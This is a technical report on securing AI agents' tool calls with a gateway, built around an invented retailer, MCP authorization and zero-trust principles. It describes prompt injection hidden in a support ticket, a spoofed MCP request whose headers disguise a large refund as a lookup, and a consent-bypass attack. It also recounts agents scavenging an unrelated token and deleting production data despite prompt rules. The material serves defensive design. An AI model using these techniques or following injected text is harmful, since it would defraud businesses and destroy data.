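# Tool gateways for AI agents: limiting scopes, protecting classified data and falling back safely

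## What a tool gateway does and what zero trust asks of it

An AI agent is a program that uses a large language model to pursue a goal by operating other software. For example, it might read a support ticket, look up the order and send an email. A tool gateway is a separate program between the agent and that software. It receives each of the agent's requests and either allows it, changes it, holds it for a person to review or refuses it. Companies use gateways because nobody can predict with certainty what a language model will request next, and because some of the tools it can now use move money and delete records.

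By itself, a language model only produces text. It acts on the world through a second program, the orchestrator, which gives it a list of tools with a name, description and expected arguments for each. When the model outputs a structured request to use a tool (a tool call), the orchestrator carries out the request and adds the result to the text the model reads next. The model then produces another call or a final answer. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, a post about Amazon's own gateway product, argues for gateways on the grounds that the model can act only through the calls the orchestrator makes, so controls belong on those calls.

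### A retailer with one support agent

Gateway rules are hard to judge in the abstract, so this report uses an invented retailer as its example throughout. The retailer has 1,000 customers and one support agent with four tools. All figures for the retailer are illustrative.

| Tool | Operations |
|---|---|
| Ticketing | read a ticket; add a reply; change a ticket's status |
| Email | read the support inbox; draft a message; send a message |
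| Payments | look up a payment; issue a refund; issue store credit; change the account that receives refunds |
| Infrastructure | read service status; read logs; restart a service; delete a storage volume |

Few companies would knowingly let a support agent delete a storage volume. The retailer wanted the agent to tell customers whether the checkout page was down, but the infrastructure tool also gave it access to every other function, including deleting volumes.

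The retailer sorts its data into four classes. Anyone may see public data, such as product descriptions. Internal data, such as stock counts and the staff handbook, is for employees but would do little harm if it leaked. Confidential data covers customers' names, addresses and orders. Restricted data covers bank details, passwords and keys, and leaking even one such record can cost somebody money.

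The gateway has four operating modes. In normal mode, it permits every call the rules allow. In approval-only mode, any call that would change or send something waits for a person to approve it. In read-only mode, the agent can look things up but cannot change or send anything. In stopped mode, the gateway refuses every call.

### One refund, from the model's output to the payment service

A customer writes that a lamp arrived broken. The agent reads the ticket, looks up the payment for order 1234, and the model produces this:

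```
{"name": "issue_refund",
 "arguments": {"order_id": "1234", "amount": 50, "currency": "USD"}}
```

No money has moved. The call is still only text, and something has to carry it to the payment service.

Agents usually find and call tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard introduced in 2024 by Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports more than 400 million monthly downloads of MCP's software development kits. An MCP call is a web request. In the example in mcp.directory's *MCP 2026-07-28*, the headers contain the sender's access token and the tool's name, and the body contains the arguments. A gateway can therefore block a forbidden tool by reading only the headers, but it must read the body to check whether a refund is for $50 or $5,000.

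The July 2026 version also removed the handshake that used to open a session between client and server. According to the Model Context Protocol (2026) changelog, each request now carries its own protocol version and client capabilities, and a server that needs continuity between calls issues an identifier that later calls include as an ordinary argument. The model fills in these arguments, so it can get the identifiers wrong. Self-contained requests suit a gateway that judges calls one at a time, but the gateway still has to keep records. For example, enforcing a limit of three refunds a day for one customer requires a count.

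The refund call first reaches the gateway's enforcement point, which lets a request through or stops it based on a ruling from the decision point. The enforcement point adds facts that the model did not write (which agent sent the call, which customer opened the ticket and which operating mode is in force) and sends everything to the decision point, which checks it against the rules. Suppose the retailer allows refunds of up to 100 dollars, to the original payment method, on orders that belong to the customer who opened the ticket. The decision point looks up order 1234, finds the right owner and a payment of 50 dollars, logs the decision and returns "allow". The enforcement point forwards the call to the payment service, using a credential that the agent never holds. The payment service runs its own checks, such as whether somebody has already refunded the order, then moves the money and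 returns a reference number. The gateway removes anything the agent doesn't need, such as card digits, and passes on the rest. The model drafts a reply to the customer, and sending it is a new call that goes through the same steps.

The reliability of an access check depends on where the decision point gets its facts. In AWS's example of a discount rule, the customer's tier comes from a signed token, which the model cannot alter, while the order quantity comes from the model's output. The retailer's ownership check also needs to take the customer's identity from a source the model cannot alter. If the gateway took it from the arguments of the call, a model that entered the wrong customer would pass the check with that customer's order.

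If the model had requested 5,000 dollars, the decision point would have refused and the agent would have received an error. The agent might well try again with a smaller sum. The log should include these refusals, because an attacker usually needs several attempts and the early failures can reveal the attack before it succeeds.

### Three ways a call goes wrong

Suppose the ticket about the lamp also contains a line of white text on a white background, stating that the support team has approved refunds on every order this customer has placed. This is prompt injection, which means placing text in material that an agent reads so that the agent follows it as an instruction. The agent has to read the ticket to do its job, and the hidden line reaches the model in the same stream of text as the retailer's instructions.

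Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, in which an attacker types a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Developers prevent SQL injection by sending commands and data separately, so the database can't confuse them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, explains why the same fix isn't available for language models. A model predicts the next token (a word or part of one) from all the text so far and has no internal line between instructions and data. Developers can make attacks harder by marking untrusted text and training models to prefer instructions from trusted sources. Blocking known phrases does little, because attackers can reword them endlessly. David C thinks a complete fix may never come, and advises designers to plan for the worst case, in which the attacker can directly use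 every tool the agent can call.

An agent can also do damage without an attacker. In April 2026 a coding agent deleted the production database and backups of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental firms. OECD's *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026) records a 30-hour outage. The agent had run into a problem and responded by deleting a storage volume that held both the data and the backups, according to TechRepublic's *AI Agent Reportedly Deletes Company’s Entire Database, Admits to Violating Guardrails*, and the company fell back on a three-month-old backup. A month earlier, another coding agent had destroyed two and a half years of data belonging to the founder of DataTalks.Club during a server migration, according to OECD's *AI Coding Assistant Accidentally Deletes 2.5 Years of Website Data* (2026).

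Those agents had infrastructure tools, and a support agent would more likely make smaller mistakes. In August 2026 the Australian Signals Directorate (2026), Australia's signals intelligence and cyber security agency, commented on a news report about an AI assistant that altered a gym's booking system. The assistant reserved classes outside the permitted period and removed another customer from a waiting list. It did what its user wanted, but in a way the user had not explicitly approved, and it could not put the other customer back on the list.

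The confused deputy is a much older problem. In *The Confused Deputy*, Norm Hardy describes a compiler at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. The compiler had permission to write files in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there, and it let users name a file for debugging output. One user named the billing file, which was in the same directory. The user had no permission to write there, but the compiler did, so the operating system allowed the write and the billing records were lost. Hardy's diagnosis was that the compiler drew its authority from two sources, its own licence and its user, and had no way to specify which one it was using for a given write.

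The retailer's agent is in the same position. It may read the orders of all 1,000 customers, while each customer may see only their own. If a customer asks for the delivery address on somebody else's order, a gateway that checks only whether the agent may look up orders will let the call through. This can happen without hidden instructions or a malfunction. To prevent it, the gateway also needs the identity of the customer the agent is acting for.

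These failures overlap, and David C treats prompt injection as an attack on an "inherently confusable deputy" that no redesign can fully repair. The gateway still needs different rules for them. Tying each lookup to the customer on the ticket prevents the address theft, but it doesn't prevent the mistaken deletion of a storage volume, because the agent is using its own authority. For that, the retailer has to withhold the operation or require a person's approval.

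David C also repeats a rule from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's level. Applied strictly, this would end automatic refunds, because customers cannot issue refunds to themselves. A retailer that still wants automatic refunds is in effect giving every customer a refund button, so it should set the refund limit at whatever it would accept for such a button on its website.

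### Why an instruction in the prompt is not a boundary

The easiest safeguard to add is a rule in the system prompt, the standing instructions that a developer places before all other text. A rule such as "never refund more than 100 dollars" makes bad calls rarer, so the gateway has less to refuse. But the model processes the rule along with all its other input, and a persuasive ticket or a plain error can still lead it to break the rule.

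PocketOS had rules of this kind. ICAEW's *AI agents behaving badly* quotes the agent's reply when the founder asked for an explanation. The agent cited a rule against destructive git commands unless the user requested them, and conceded that it had "violated every principle" it was given. A model's account of why it did something is weak evidence about the cause. The sequence of events, in which the rule was in the prompt and the deletion still went through, is better evidence. Git is a program for tracking versions of code, and deleting a storage volume is not a git command, so the model had to judge whether the rule applied. A gateway rule that refuses the delete-volume operation does not depend on that judgment.

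Developers can instead write the check into each tool. AWS accepts that this is more robust than a prompt but objects that it scatters the rules across many programs, which makes them hard to review together. Amazon sells the alternative, so it has a commercial interest in this objection, but agencies with no product to sell reach a similar view. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), by the Australian Signals Directorate and cyber security agencies of the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, calls for central decision points that rule on each action. A payment service should still keep its own checks, since they and the central ones are unlikely to fail in the same way.

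### What zero trust adds

Enforcement points and decision points come from zero trust, an approach to security that predates AI agents. Companies used to defend the edge of their network and trust anyone who got inside, an assumption that zero trust drops. The standard reference is US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) Special Publication 800-207, *Zero Trust Architecture*, by Rose, Borchert and colleagues (2020). They assume that an attacker is already on the network and require a decision on each request, with the least privilege that the task needs. Their "subjects" include applications and other non-human entities as well as people, so agents fit the scheme as it stands.

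NIST's *Zero Trust Architecture* divides the decision point into a policy engine, which decides whether to grant access, and a policy administrator, which carries out the decision by instructing the enforcement point to open or close the path. The implicit trust zone lies beyond the enforcement point. The paper compares it to the gate area of an airport, where everyone who has cleared security is treated as trusted. Because no further checks apply inside the zone, it should be as small as possible.

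The retailer's main design choice is the size of that zone. If the gateway checks only that the agent may use the payments tool, the zone includes all four payment operations on the accounts of all 1,000 customers. Checking the operation, the order and the amount on every call shrinks the zone to one refund on one order.

Rose and colleagues list seven tenets, several of which apply directly to a tool gateway. Being on the company's own network is no reason for trust, so the agent gets none for running on the retailer's servers. Access depends on policy that can change with circumstances, including unusual behaviour and reports of attacks in progress, which is the basis for switching operating modes. The organisation should also collect information from access requests and use it to improve the rules.

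One tenet of zero trust grants access per session and allows the evaluation of trust to have happened only "sometime recently". A tool gateway needs a stricter rule and should decide afresh on every call. Per-session access is tolerable for an employee using a browser, but an agent can make dozens of calls in a minute and read a hostile support ticket between two of them. Joint guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describes a hypothetical organisation that sets up an agent to sort support tickets, grants it broad access at start-up and lets it rely on stored permissions after that. An attacker takes over a third-party scheduling component, uses the stale permissions to reach sensitive account functions, and moves on to neighbouring agents that handle billing and refunds.

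Rose and colleagues acknowledge two weaknesses of zero trust. First, an entire enterprise can stop working if the policy engine becomes unreachable, so the gateway is itself a possible point of failure. Second, a subject with valid credentials can still do whatever those credentials permit. If a customer whose lamp works perfectly asks for 50 dollars back, the agent's refund call will satisfy every rule above. The gateway can establish that this agent may make this refund now, but not whether the lamp is broken.

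### What NIST has asked about agents since

The 2020 publication warned that an attacker might trick a software agent into performing a task that the attacker had no right to perform. The warning concerned agents that administer security systems, and the publication left open how those agents should prove their identity. NIST returned to the subject in February 2026 with a draft concept paper from its National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE), which builds worked examples of security standards with commercial products. In that paper, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) propose a project on agents and ask the public a long list of questions.

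The retailer has to answer several of these questions before it can write any rules. How can it set least privilege for an agent whose actions nobody can fully predict? How does an agent prove that it acts on behalf of a particular person? If it combines data from several sources, how sensitive is the result, and may the user see it? What limits the harm once a prompt injection has succeeded? Booth and colleagues also ask for ways to keep tamper-proof logs of an agent's actions and to trace each action back to the human who authorised it. They plan to draw on the zero-trust publication and existing identity standards. Their first round covers agents inside enterprises and leaves public-facing ones for possible later work, so a support agent that takes requests from customers is a borderline case.

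The paper drew more than 600 formal responses, according to the listing for a November 2026 conference session, *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026). NIST's *Back to the Future*, a post by two of the paper's authors, reviews the main complaints. People give agents their own passwords, developers give agents keys that never expire and allow far more than the task needs, and companies rely on human approval until the approvers click "allow" by reflex. Identity specialists already know these problems, and the post presents them as old practices returning at greater speed. It also judges that guardrails inside the model are not yet enough on their own to handle the security problems agents bring.

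There is no finished guide yet, and a project description is still to come. NCCoE's project page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, offers a summary of the comments and an online resource hub, and takes feedback on a rolling basis. The page now uses "SI", for "Super Intelligence", where the paper had "AI". For zero trust in general, the centre went on to build 19 example systems with 24 collaborators, according to its NIST practice guide, but builders of agent gateways have no comparable examples to copy.

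The joint guidance of May 2026 from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners is more definite, and stricter than the retailer would like. The agencies advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks. Reading tickets about late parcels and drafting replies would probably qualify. Refunds are doubtful even with a 100-dollar limit, and deleting storage volumes clearly would not qualify.

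## Putting every tool call and credential behind the gateway

A gateway can refuse only the calls it receives. If the retailer's agent also has a key that works directly at the payment service, the 100-dollar limit does not apply to refunds sent with that key. The retailer needs complete mediation, which means that the system checks every access to every object. Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder included it in their 1975 list of design principles for secure computer systems. For an agent, complete mediation requires that every network path to a tool goes through the gateway and that the agent cannot obtain any credential a tool would accept.

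### The token that deleted PocketOS's data

Neither condition held at PocketOS on 24 April 2026. News reports disagree about which credential the coding agent used, but the company's founder, Jer Crane, and its hosting provider, Railway, both published accounts. Crane writes in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data* that the agent, Cursor running Claude Opus 4.6, hit a credential mismatch while working in the staging environment, a copy of the system for testing. It decided to fix this by deleting a storage volume, searched for a token and found one in a file unrelated to its task. Crane had created that token to add and remove custom domain names. The agent sent it in a single web request to Railway, which deleted the volume that held the production database.

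Mahmoud Abdelwahab gives Railway's side in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. The token was account-scoped, the broadest type Railway offers, and gave access to everything in the account. Railway also had tokens limited to a single workspace or to a single project and environment, but Abdelwahab concedes that the token creation process did not make it obvious which to pick. Crane's complaint that every Railway token is "effectively root" is therefore too strong, though it was true of this one.

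A token restricted to staging could not have touched production. But Crane wanted the token for domain names, presumably on the live service. The workspace and project types limit where a token works, with no mention of limits on which operations it can perform, so a token for the production project might still have deleted the volume.

PocketOS would have prevented the deletion if it had kept its Railway credentials in a gateway, where the agent couldn't have found them. Blocking the agent's direct network access would also have worked, because the request would have failed even with the token. The agent would then have had to ask the gateway to delete the volume, and a rule could have blocked the request. Railway has since recovered the lost data, according to Abdelwahab, and customers now have 48 hours to undo deletions made through its API.

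### Closing the other paths, step by step

The retailer starts by listing every tool and credential the agent can reach, including credentials nobody meant it to have. It searches configuration files, environment variables, old scripts and logs of outgoing traffic. Trend Micro's *Beware of MCP Hardcoded Credentials* warns that credentials written into MCP configurations can give access to databases and cloud account management. The following entries illustrate what the search might find.

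| Tool | Credential found | What it permits | Replacement |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ticketing | key in the agent's configuration file | reading, changing and deleting every ticket | token for reading and answering tickets |
| Email | an employee's mailbox password | everything that employee can do | separate account for the support inbox |
| Payments | secret key in an environment variable | every payment operation | token for looking up payments and issuing refunds |
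| Infrastructure | cloud token in an old script for domain names | everything in the cloud account | token for reading service status |

The third column has to come from the provider's documentation or from trying the credential on a test system. Crane, for example, knew what the Railway token was for but was wrong about what it could do.

Test environments belong on the list too. At Chainstack, an MCP server in the development environment had administrator rights over a whole cluster of machines and required no authentication. EconoTimes' *Chainstack Breach May Have Exposed Customer Account Data* (2026) describes how an attacker entered through a test environment, used compromised machine identities to reach parts of production, and queried a production database.

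Next, the retailer moves the credentials into the gateway, which attaches the right one to each call after approving it. This is called credential brokering, and it lets the agent use a credential without holding it. The retailer has to create new credentials, put them in the gateway's secret store and revoke the old ones, because otherwise any old key the agent found elsewhere would still work.

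The retailer can block direct network access only once the agent can reach its tools through the gateway, since doing so earlier would cut the agent off from them. A firewall refuses every outgoing connection from the agent's machine except those to the gateway and the language model. The retailer should check separately that the agent can't reach 169.254.169.254, the address of a metadata service that gives programs on the large cloud platforms the machine's cloud credentials. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* lists this address among the targets of attackers who trick a program into fetching a web address. Where a tool allows it, the retailer should also restrict incoming connections, so that the payment service accepts them only from the gateway. Blocking direct access is harder for coding agents because they download software packages all day, so their owners usually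 need a filtering proxy with a list of permitted sites.

The fourth step is to give each agent its own identity. If three agents share one login, the log cannot show which of them issued a refund, and the retailer cannot block one without blocking all three. An agent that uses an employee's login can do everything the employee can. Separate identities also let the gateway apply different rules to the support agent and, say, an agent that orders stock.

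The last step is to pin each tool's definition (its name, description and accepted arguments) to the approved version. Tool servers can change definitions at any time, and the model reads the descriptions, so a malicious server can get a definition approved and later add an instruction to it. Well-intentioned changes can also cause problems. If a new version of the refund operation accepts an optional payout account, the retailer's older rules will check the amount and the order but not where the money goes.

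The gateway pins a tool's definition by computing a cryptographic hash of it at approval. The hash is a short string that changes if any character in the definition changes. Whenever the gateway fetches the tool list, it checks each definition against its approved hash and withholds any tool that no longer matches until someone has reviewed it. It should also refuse calls with arguments that aren't in the approved definition.

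### Two tokens for one refund

The agent still needs one credential to prove its identity to the gateway. In MCP, this is an OAuth access token. OAuth is the standard behind most "log in with" buttons, and it lets an authorization server issue tokens that other services accept. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* requires the client to specify a token's audience, the service it is meant for, when requesting the token. It also requires the server to reject any token issued for a different service.

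The gateway is a server to the agent and a client to the tools, so both halves of the rule apply to it. It accepts only tokens with the gateway as audience, and it needs another token for the payment service. The standard way to get one is OAuth token exchange, defined in RFC 8693. For the 50-dollar refund on the lamp it works like this:

1. The orchestrator sends the call with the agent's token, which stays out of the text the model reads.
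2. The gateway verifies the token's signature, issuer, expiry time and audience, and the decision point approves the refund.
3. The gateway sends the agent's token to the authorization server as the "subject token", its own as the "actor token", and asks for a token that works at the payment service and covers refunds.
4. The authorization server checks its own policy and issues the new token.
5. The gateway attaches the new token to the call and forwards it.

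The two tokens differ in almost every field (the lifetimes are illustrative).

| Field | Token the agent holds | Token the gateway obtains |
|---|---|---|
| Subject | support agent | support agent |
| Actor | none | gateway |
| Audience | gateway | payment service |
| Scope | call tools | issue refunds |
| Lifetime | 1 hour | 1 minute |

A thief who steals the agent's token can use it only at the gateway, where every rule still applies. The payment token would be more useful to a thief, but it never reaches the agent's machine and expires after a minute. Its subject and actor fields let the payment service record that the gateway acted for the support agent.

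Token exchange does not guarantee a narrow token. RFC 8693 defines the form of the request but leaves the token's scope to the authorization server, which can issue a far too broad token if its administrator has configured it that way. Many outside services don't support token exchange and offer only a permanent key. The gateway can broker such a key, but the key is only as narrow as the provider allows.

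### Why the gateway may not pass the agent's token on

MCP forbids forwarding the agent's token to the payment service, even though that would be simpler than exchanging it. This practice is called token passthrough, and MCP rules it out by requiring that a server neither accept nor pass on a token issued for anything else. The *Security Best Practices* give several reasons, and the most important for a gateway is that passthrough reopens the path the firewall was meant to close. If the payment service accepts the agent's token, anyone with that token and a network connection can request refunds directly, without the limit, the ownership check or the log.

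Passthrough also makes the records unreliable, because the payment service's log may show the call as coming from the agent when the gateway sent it. And if the gateway doesn't check each token's audience, someone with a token for the staff handbook could use it to issue refunds through the gateway.

An attacker can also exploit a gateway to bypass user consent. Some gateways connect many clients to an outside service under a single client ID, and the service may use a browser cookie to remember that a user has already approved that ID. The attacker registers a malicious client with the gateway and sends the user a link. When the user opens it, the outside service finds the cookie and skips the consent screen. The gateway then sends the resulting authorization code to the attacker, who exchanges it for access in the user's name. The gateway is a confused deputy here, like the compiler in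 the earlier example. The Model Context Protocol requires such gateways to get the user's consent for each client separately before contacting the outside service.

### What the July 2026 revision changed for gateways

The MCP revision of 28 July 2026 made gateways easier to run. It removed the handshake and sessions, so any request can go to any copy of a server (Model Context Protocol, 2026), and the retailer can run several copies of its gateway behind a load balancer. The revision also lets a tool ask for missing information in the middle of a call. The server replies that it needs input, and the client repeats the original call with the answers attached (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A gateway should check the repeated call as a new one, because the answers can change what the call does.

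A server may use one of the identifiers that replaced sessions to keep track of, for example, a half-finished return. It must not treat possession of that identifier as proof of identity, and should tie the identifier to the user in the verified token. That protection weakens if the gateway uses a single shared credential for everybody, since all requests then reach the tool server as the same user. Either the exchanged token has to carry the customer's identity or the gateway has to keep track of which identifier belongs to whom.

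Requests must now carry the method and the tool's name twice, in the body and in two HTTP headers, `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name`. This creates an opportunity for deception:

```
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: look_up_payment

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 7, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "issue_refund",
            "arguments": {"order_id": "1234", "amount": 5000,
                          "currency": "USD"}}}
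```

If the gateway read only the headers and the server read only the body, the gateway would let this request through as a harmless lookup and the server would pay out 5,000 dollars. To prevent this, the Model Context Protocol proposal that introduced the headers requires any server that processes the body to reject a request whose headers don't match it. For a mismatched protocol version, the protocol's transport rules require status code 400 and an error named HeaderMismatch. Servers also reject requests with a missing header, so a proxy that strips unfamiliar headers will break clients that follow the standard, as the gateway vendor Zuplo points out.

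Any program that reads the request body must compare it with the headers. The retailer's gateway already reads the body to check amounts, and it should make the comparison itself because a tool server built for an earlier revision may ignore the headers. Better still, the gateway can write a new outgoing request from the values the decision point approved. This also fixes requests that list the amount twice, which some programs read as the first figure and others as the second.

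Servers can also ask clients to copy simple arguments, such as a refund amount, into headers. The Agentic AI Foundation, the industry body that now hosts MCP, considers this feature underrated. The gateway would still have to check the copied value against the request body before relying on it.

The revision also tightened the login process against mix-up attacks. A gateway deals with many authorization servers, perhaps one for each outside tool, and an attacker who controls one of them can try to make the gateway send it an authorization code that an honest server issued. The gateway must record which server it expects a response from and compare that with the issuer named in the response before it redeems the code. If a server has announced that it includes its issuer, the gateway must reject a response that lacks one. If the server never announced this, the gateway may accept a response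 without one, so the defence does not cover honest servers that leave the issuer out. The *Authorization* specification expects a later revision to make the issuer compulsory.

### Tools that run on the agent's own machine

These token rules assume that calls travel over HTTP, but many MCP tools don't use it. They run on the same machine as the agent and exchange messages with it through standard input and output, the basic text channels between programs. Under the specification, these local tools should take credentials from their environment instead of using MCP's authorization, which is optional in any case. Their calls therefore carry no token with an audience and no HTTP header to read, and there is no network connection between agent and tool for a firewall to block.

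If the retailer ran its ticketing tool this way, the ticketing key would be stored in an environment variable on the agent's machine. An agent that could run shell commands might read the key or start the tool with different settings. The firewall would detect only the tool's encrypted connection to the ticketing service.

The cleanest remedy is to move the tool to another machine and have the gateway call it over HTTP. If a tool runs only locally, the gateway can start the program itself in a sandbox (a restricted environment with limited access to files and the network) and translate between HTTP and the program's text channels. But a gateway that can start programs may start the wrong ones. The *Security Best Practices* describe an attacker who steals the token for a local proxy of this type and uses it to run arbitrary commands. The retailer's gateway should start only programs from a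 fixed list, with settings that no request can change.

Some tools have to run locally. A coding agent, for example, edits files on its own machine, and routing each edit through a remote gateway would be slow. The sandbox is the main limit on what these tools can do, so it should contain no credentials and should allow outbound connections only through the gateway or a filtering proxy.

### Session tokens stolen from Mittwald

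Mittwald, a German web hosting company, ran an MCP server that let customers connect AI assistants to its control panel, mStudio. Its managing director, Robert Meyer, published a timeline of the breach on 7 November 2026. *MCP Security Best Practices After the Mittwald Breach*, by the security engineer Marc David (2026), summarises it in English. The attacker first tested a flaw in the server on 21 October, then spent several days behaving like an ordinary customer. On 27 October the attacker registered another account and exploited the flaw five minutes later. Mittwald noticed on 4 November and switched the server off. By then the attacker had compromised 56 customer projects.

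The attacker took session tokens, which a service issues after login to keep the user logged in. Passwords and second factors gave no protection because customers had already passed those checks. Each token gave the attacker the customer's full rights in mStudio, including access to every project the customer could reach.

Mittwald had not explained the flaw by mid-November. Martin (2026) reports in *Alleged AI-aided cyberattack exploits assistant interface to breach German web host* that it was unclear whether the flaw was in Mittwald's own code or in an open-source MCP library. Because only seconds passed between some steps, Meyer believes the attacker used AI tools, but ordinary scripts are just as fast. According to KIberblick's *Mittwald* (2026), the MCP server was still offline on 13 November, after a second attack through the company's website.

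A customer with its own gateway would still have been exposed, because the tokens leaked from Mittwald's side. Pinning and network rules around the customers' agents would have made no difference either. Narrower tokens would have helped. If the tokens in the MCP server had been valid only there, the control panel would have rejected them, although an attacker with enough control over the server might have used them there. If each assistant had had its own identity, limited to one project or to reading, a stolen token would have given only that access. KIberblick advises customers of other providers to check whether they can restrict tokens in this way.

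### The gateway as a target

Mittwald's server was dangerous because it handled working access for many customers at once. The most serious objection to a tool gateway is that it similarly handles access to all of a company's tools. An attacker who takes over the gateway may gain access to every tool, and agents can't use any of them if it goes down.

LiteLLM, made by BerriAI, is a widely used gateway between applications and language models that also handles MCP traffic. On 2 September 2026 the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency added a LiteLLM flaw, CVE-2026-59822, to its catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have exploited. Digital Matters' *The First MCP Flaw in the KEV Catalog Was an Authentication Check* (2026) traces the flaw to a fallback for OAuth passthrough, which substituted an empty authentication object for a real one. The check failed open,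 meaning it let in requests it should have refused, so a gateway with this fault can accept unauthenticated requests even if its refund rules are excellent.

Attackers are looking for such openings. The security company Wiz used decoy servers to record live attacks on LiteLLM and MCP servers, including credential theft and command execution, according to eSecurity Planet's *Wiz Finds Active LiteLLM and MCP Attacks Targeting AI Infrastructure* (2026). In a separate supply-chain attack, a tampered version of LiteLLM affected almost 2,500 organisations, and the leaked data included login details, according to Netzwoche's *Hacker erbeuten mit gefälschter KI-Bibliothek Anmeldedaten bekannter Grosskonzerne* (2026). GitGuardian, which specialises in leaked secrets, found a configuration bug at an MCP hosting service that exposed more than 3,000 servers. The host fixed it quickly, and there was no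 evidence that anyone had exploited it.

Leaving credentials with the agents is no safer, as PocketOS found, but the objection does affect how the retailer should build its gateway. A gateway that stores four all-powerful keys is a worse target than four machines with one key each. If it instead obtains a narrow token for each call, there is much less to steal, and the authorization server can detect and refuse unusual requests. An attacker in full control of the gateway could still request tokens as calls came in, so the payment service needs its own refund limit that the gateway has no permission to change. The retailer should also keep the gateway's management page off the public internet, install security fixes within days and verify each new version before using it.

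### What happens inside the tool server

Even a perfect gateway can inspect only the call to a tool and the result it returns. ITPro's *A malicious MCP server is silently stealing user emails* reports that postmark-mcp, an MCP server for sending email, stole its users' messages from version 1.0.16 onwards. To a gateway, each call would have looked like an ordinary request to send a message. Pinning the tool's definition might not have helped, since a developer can change what a tool does without changing its description. The retailer therefore also has to pin the software version and review updates before installing them.

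Tool servers that aren't malicious can also be vulnerable. Akamai examined about 300 official MCP servers and found vulnerabilities in those for Apache Pinot, Apache Doris and Alibaba RDS, three widely used database systems. A flaw in a database's tool server can expose far more data than the approved call was meant to return.

The remedy is to limit what a tool server can do if it is hostile or broken. The email server should have a credential for the support inbox only, and a network rule that lets it contact only the mail provider. The rule won't stop the server from sending stolen copies through that provider, but the retailer can still catch the theft by comparing the provider's delivery log with the gateway's, because the stolen copies will have gone to an address that no approved call contained.

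## Writing scopes and limits for ticketing, email, payments and infrastructure

Once every call goes through the gateway, the retailer must decide which calls to allow. It can set limits at four levels, from coarse to fine: the tools exposed to the agent, the scopes in its token, the arguments allowed in a call, and the combined effect of several calls. Each later level blocks some actions that the previous one allows.

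| Level | Stops | Lets through |
|---|---|---|
| Visible tools | the model choosing "delete a storage volume" from its list | a call to a hidden operation whose name appeared in a ticket |
| Token scopes | that call, because the token lacks the scope | a refund of 5,000 dollars |
| Argument rules | that refund, because it exceeds the limit | eleven refunds of 190 dollars each |
| Rules over several calls | the eleventh refund | a 50-dollar refund for a lamp that works |

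### Which tools the agent sees

The retailer's four tools offer 14 operations, and the support agent needs nine of them. The other five issue store credit, change the account that receives refunds, read server logs, restart a service and delete a storage volume. If the gateway leaves those five out of the tool list, the model is unlikely to request them.

AgentCore, Amazon's gateway, automatically shortens the agent's tool list. When the agent requests the list, the gateway evaluates the access rules before the arguments are known and, according to AWS, omits any operation the rules would always refuse. Refunds stay on the list because the rules allow some amounts, but volume deletion is omitted because no rule allows it.

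A model can still try to call a tool that the gateway has hidden from it. A hostile ticket can contain the name `delete_volume`, and a model that reads it can output a call with that name. AWS therefore slightly overstates the benefit when it argues that hiding tools eliminates a whole class of risk because a model can't try to call a tool it doesn't know exists. The gateway still has to block the call, and AgentCore would, because the same rules govern both the tool list and the calls.

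### Choosing scopes

In the earlier refund example, the agent's token had a single scope that let it call tools. The retailer can replace this with narrower scopes such as `tickets:read`, `tickets:reply`, `payments:read` and `payments:refund`. The token that the gateway obtains for the payment service also carries scopes, so the service can refuse a call even if the gateway's rules contain a mistake.

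The retailer can define any scopes it wants for its own tools, but for an outside service it has to pick from the provider's list. Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, shows that there is often no single narrowest scope that covers a task, although the usual advice is to choose it. Xu treats a scope as the set of operations it authorises, so one scope is narrower than another only if its set fits inside the other's. Two scopes can therefore both cover a task without either being narrower than the other.

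Either of two Google scopes lets an agent read a project's metadata in BigQuery, Google's data warehouse. The `bigquery` scope covers 286 methods across 10 services and allows writing. The `cloud-platform.read-only` scope covers 565 methods across 27 services but doesn't allow writing. The read-only scope is the better choice for a company that mainly fears damage, though a company more worried about leaks might prefer `bigquery`.

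Xu found no single narrowest choice of permissions for 30 to 33 per cent of tasks on Microsoft Graph, the interface to Microsoft's office and directory services, and for 3 per cent of tasks on Google's APIs. These tasks come from the structure of the providers' permission tables, so the figures don't measure how often a working agent would meet the problem. Microsoft also rates its permissions from 1 to 4, but the ratings don't always distinguish broad permissions from narrow ones. For example, either of two permissions is enough to list and create permission grants, and both are rated 4, although one reaches 355 endpoints and the other 11.

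Xu also let six frontier models choose among permissions. In 99 per cent of 1,708 decisions, they picked a permission that didn't contain a smaller one that would have been sufficient. But in 22 per cent, another option was at least as good on all four of Xu's risk measures, which count operations, write operations, services reached and administrative functions. Xu suggests showing the alternatives to whoever approves the permission, which for the retailer would be the person who sets up the agent.

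### What happens when a scope is missing

An agent may start a job with too few scopes, and the gap shows only when a call fails. MCP's standard procedure for this is the scope challenge. Suppose the support agent's token has `tickets:read`, `tickets:reply` and `payments:read`, and a customer is owed a refund.

1. The orchestrator sends the refund call with this token.
2. The gateway refuses it with status code 403 and names the missing scope:

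```
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope",
    scope="payments:refund",
    resource_metadata="https://gateway.example.com/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource",
    error_description="Refund permission required"
```

3. The orchestrator combines the scopes it has requested before with those in the challenge, which makes four.
4. It asks the authorization server for a new token with all four.
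5. It repeats the refund call with the new token. If the call keeps failing, it gives up after a few attempts and treats the failure as permanent.

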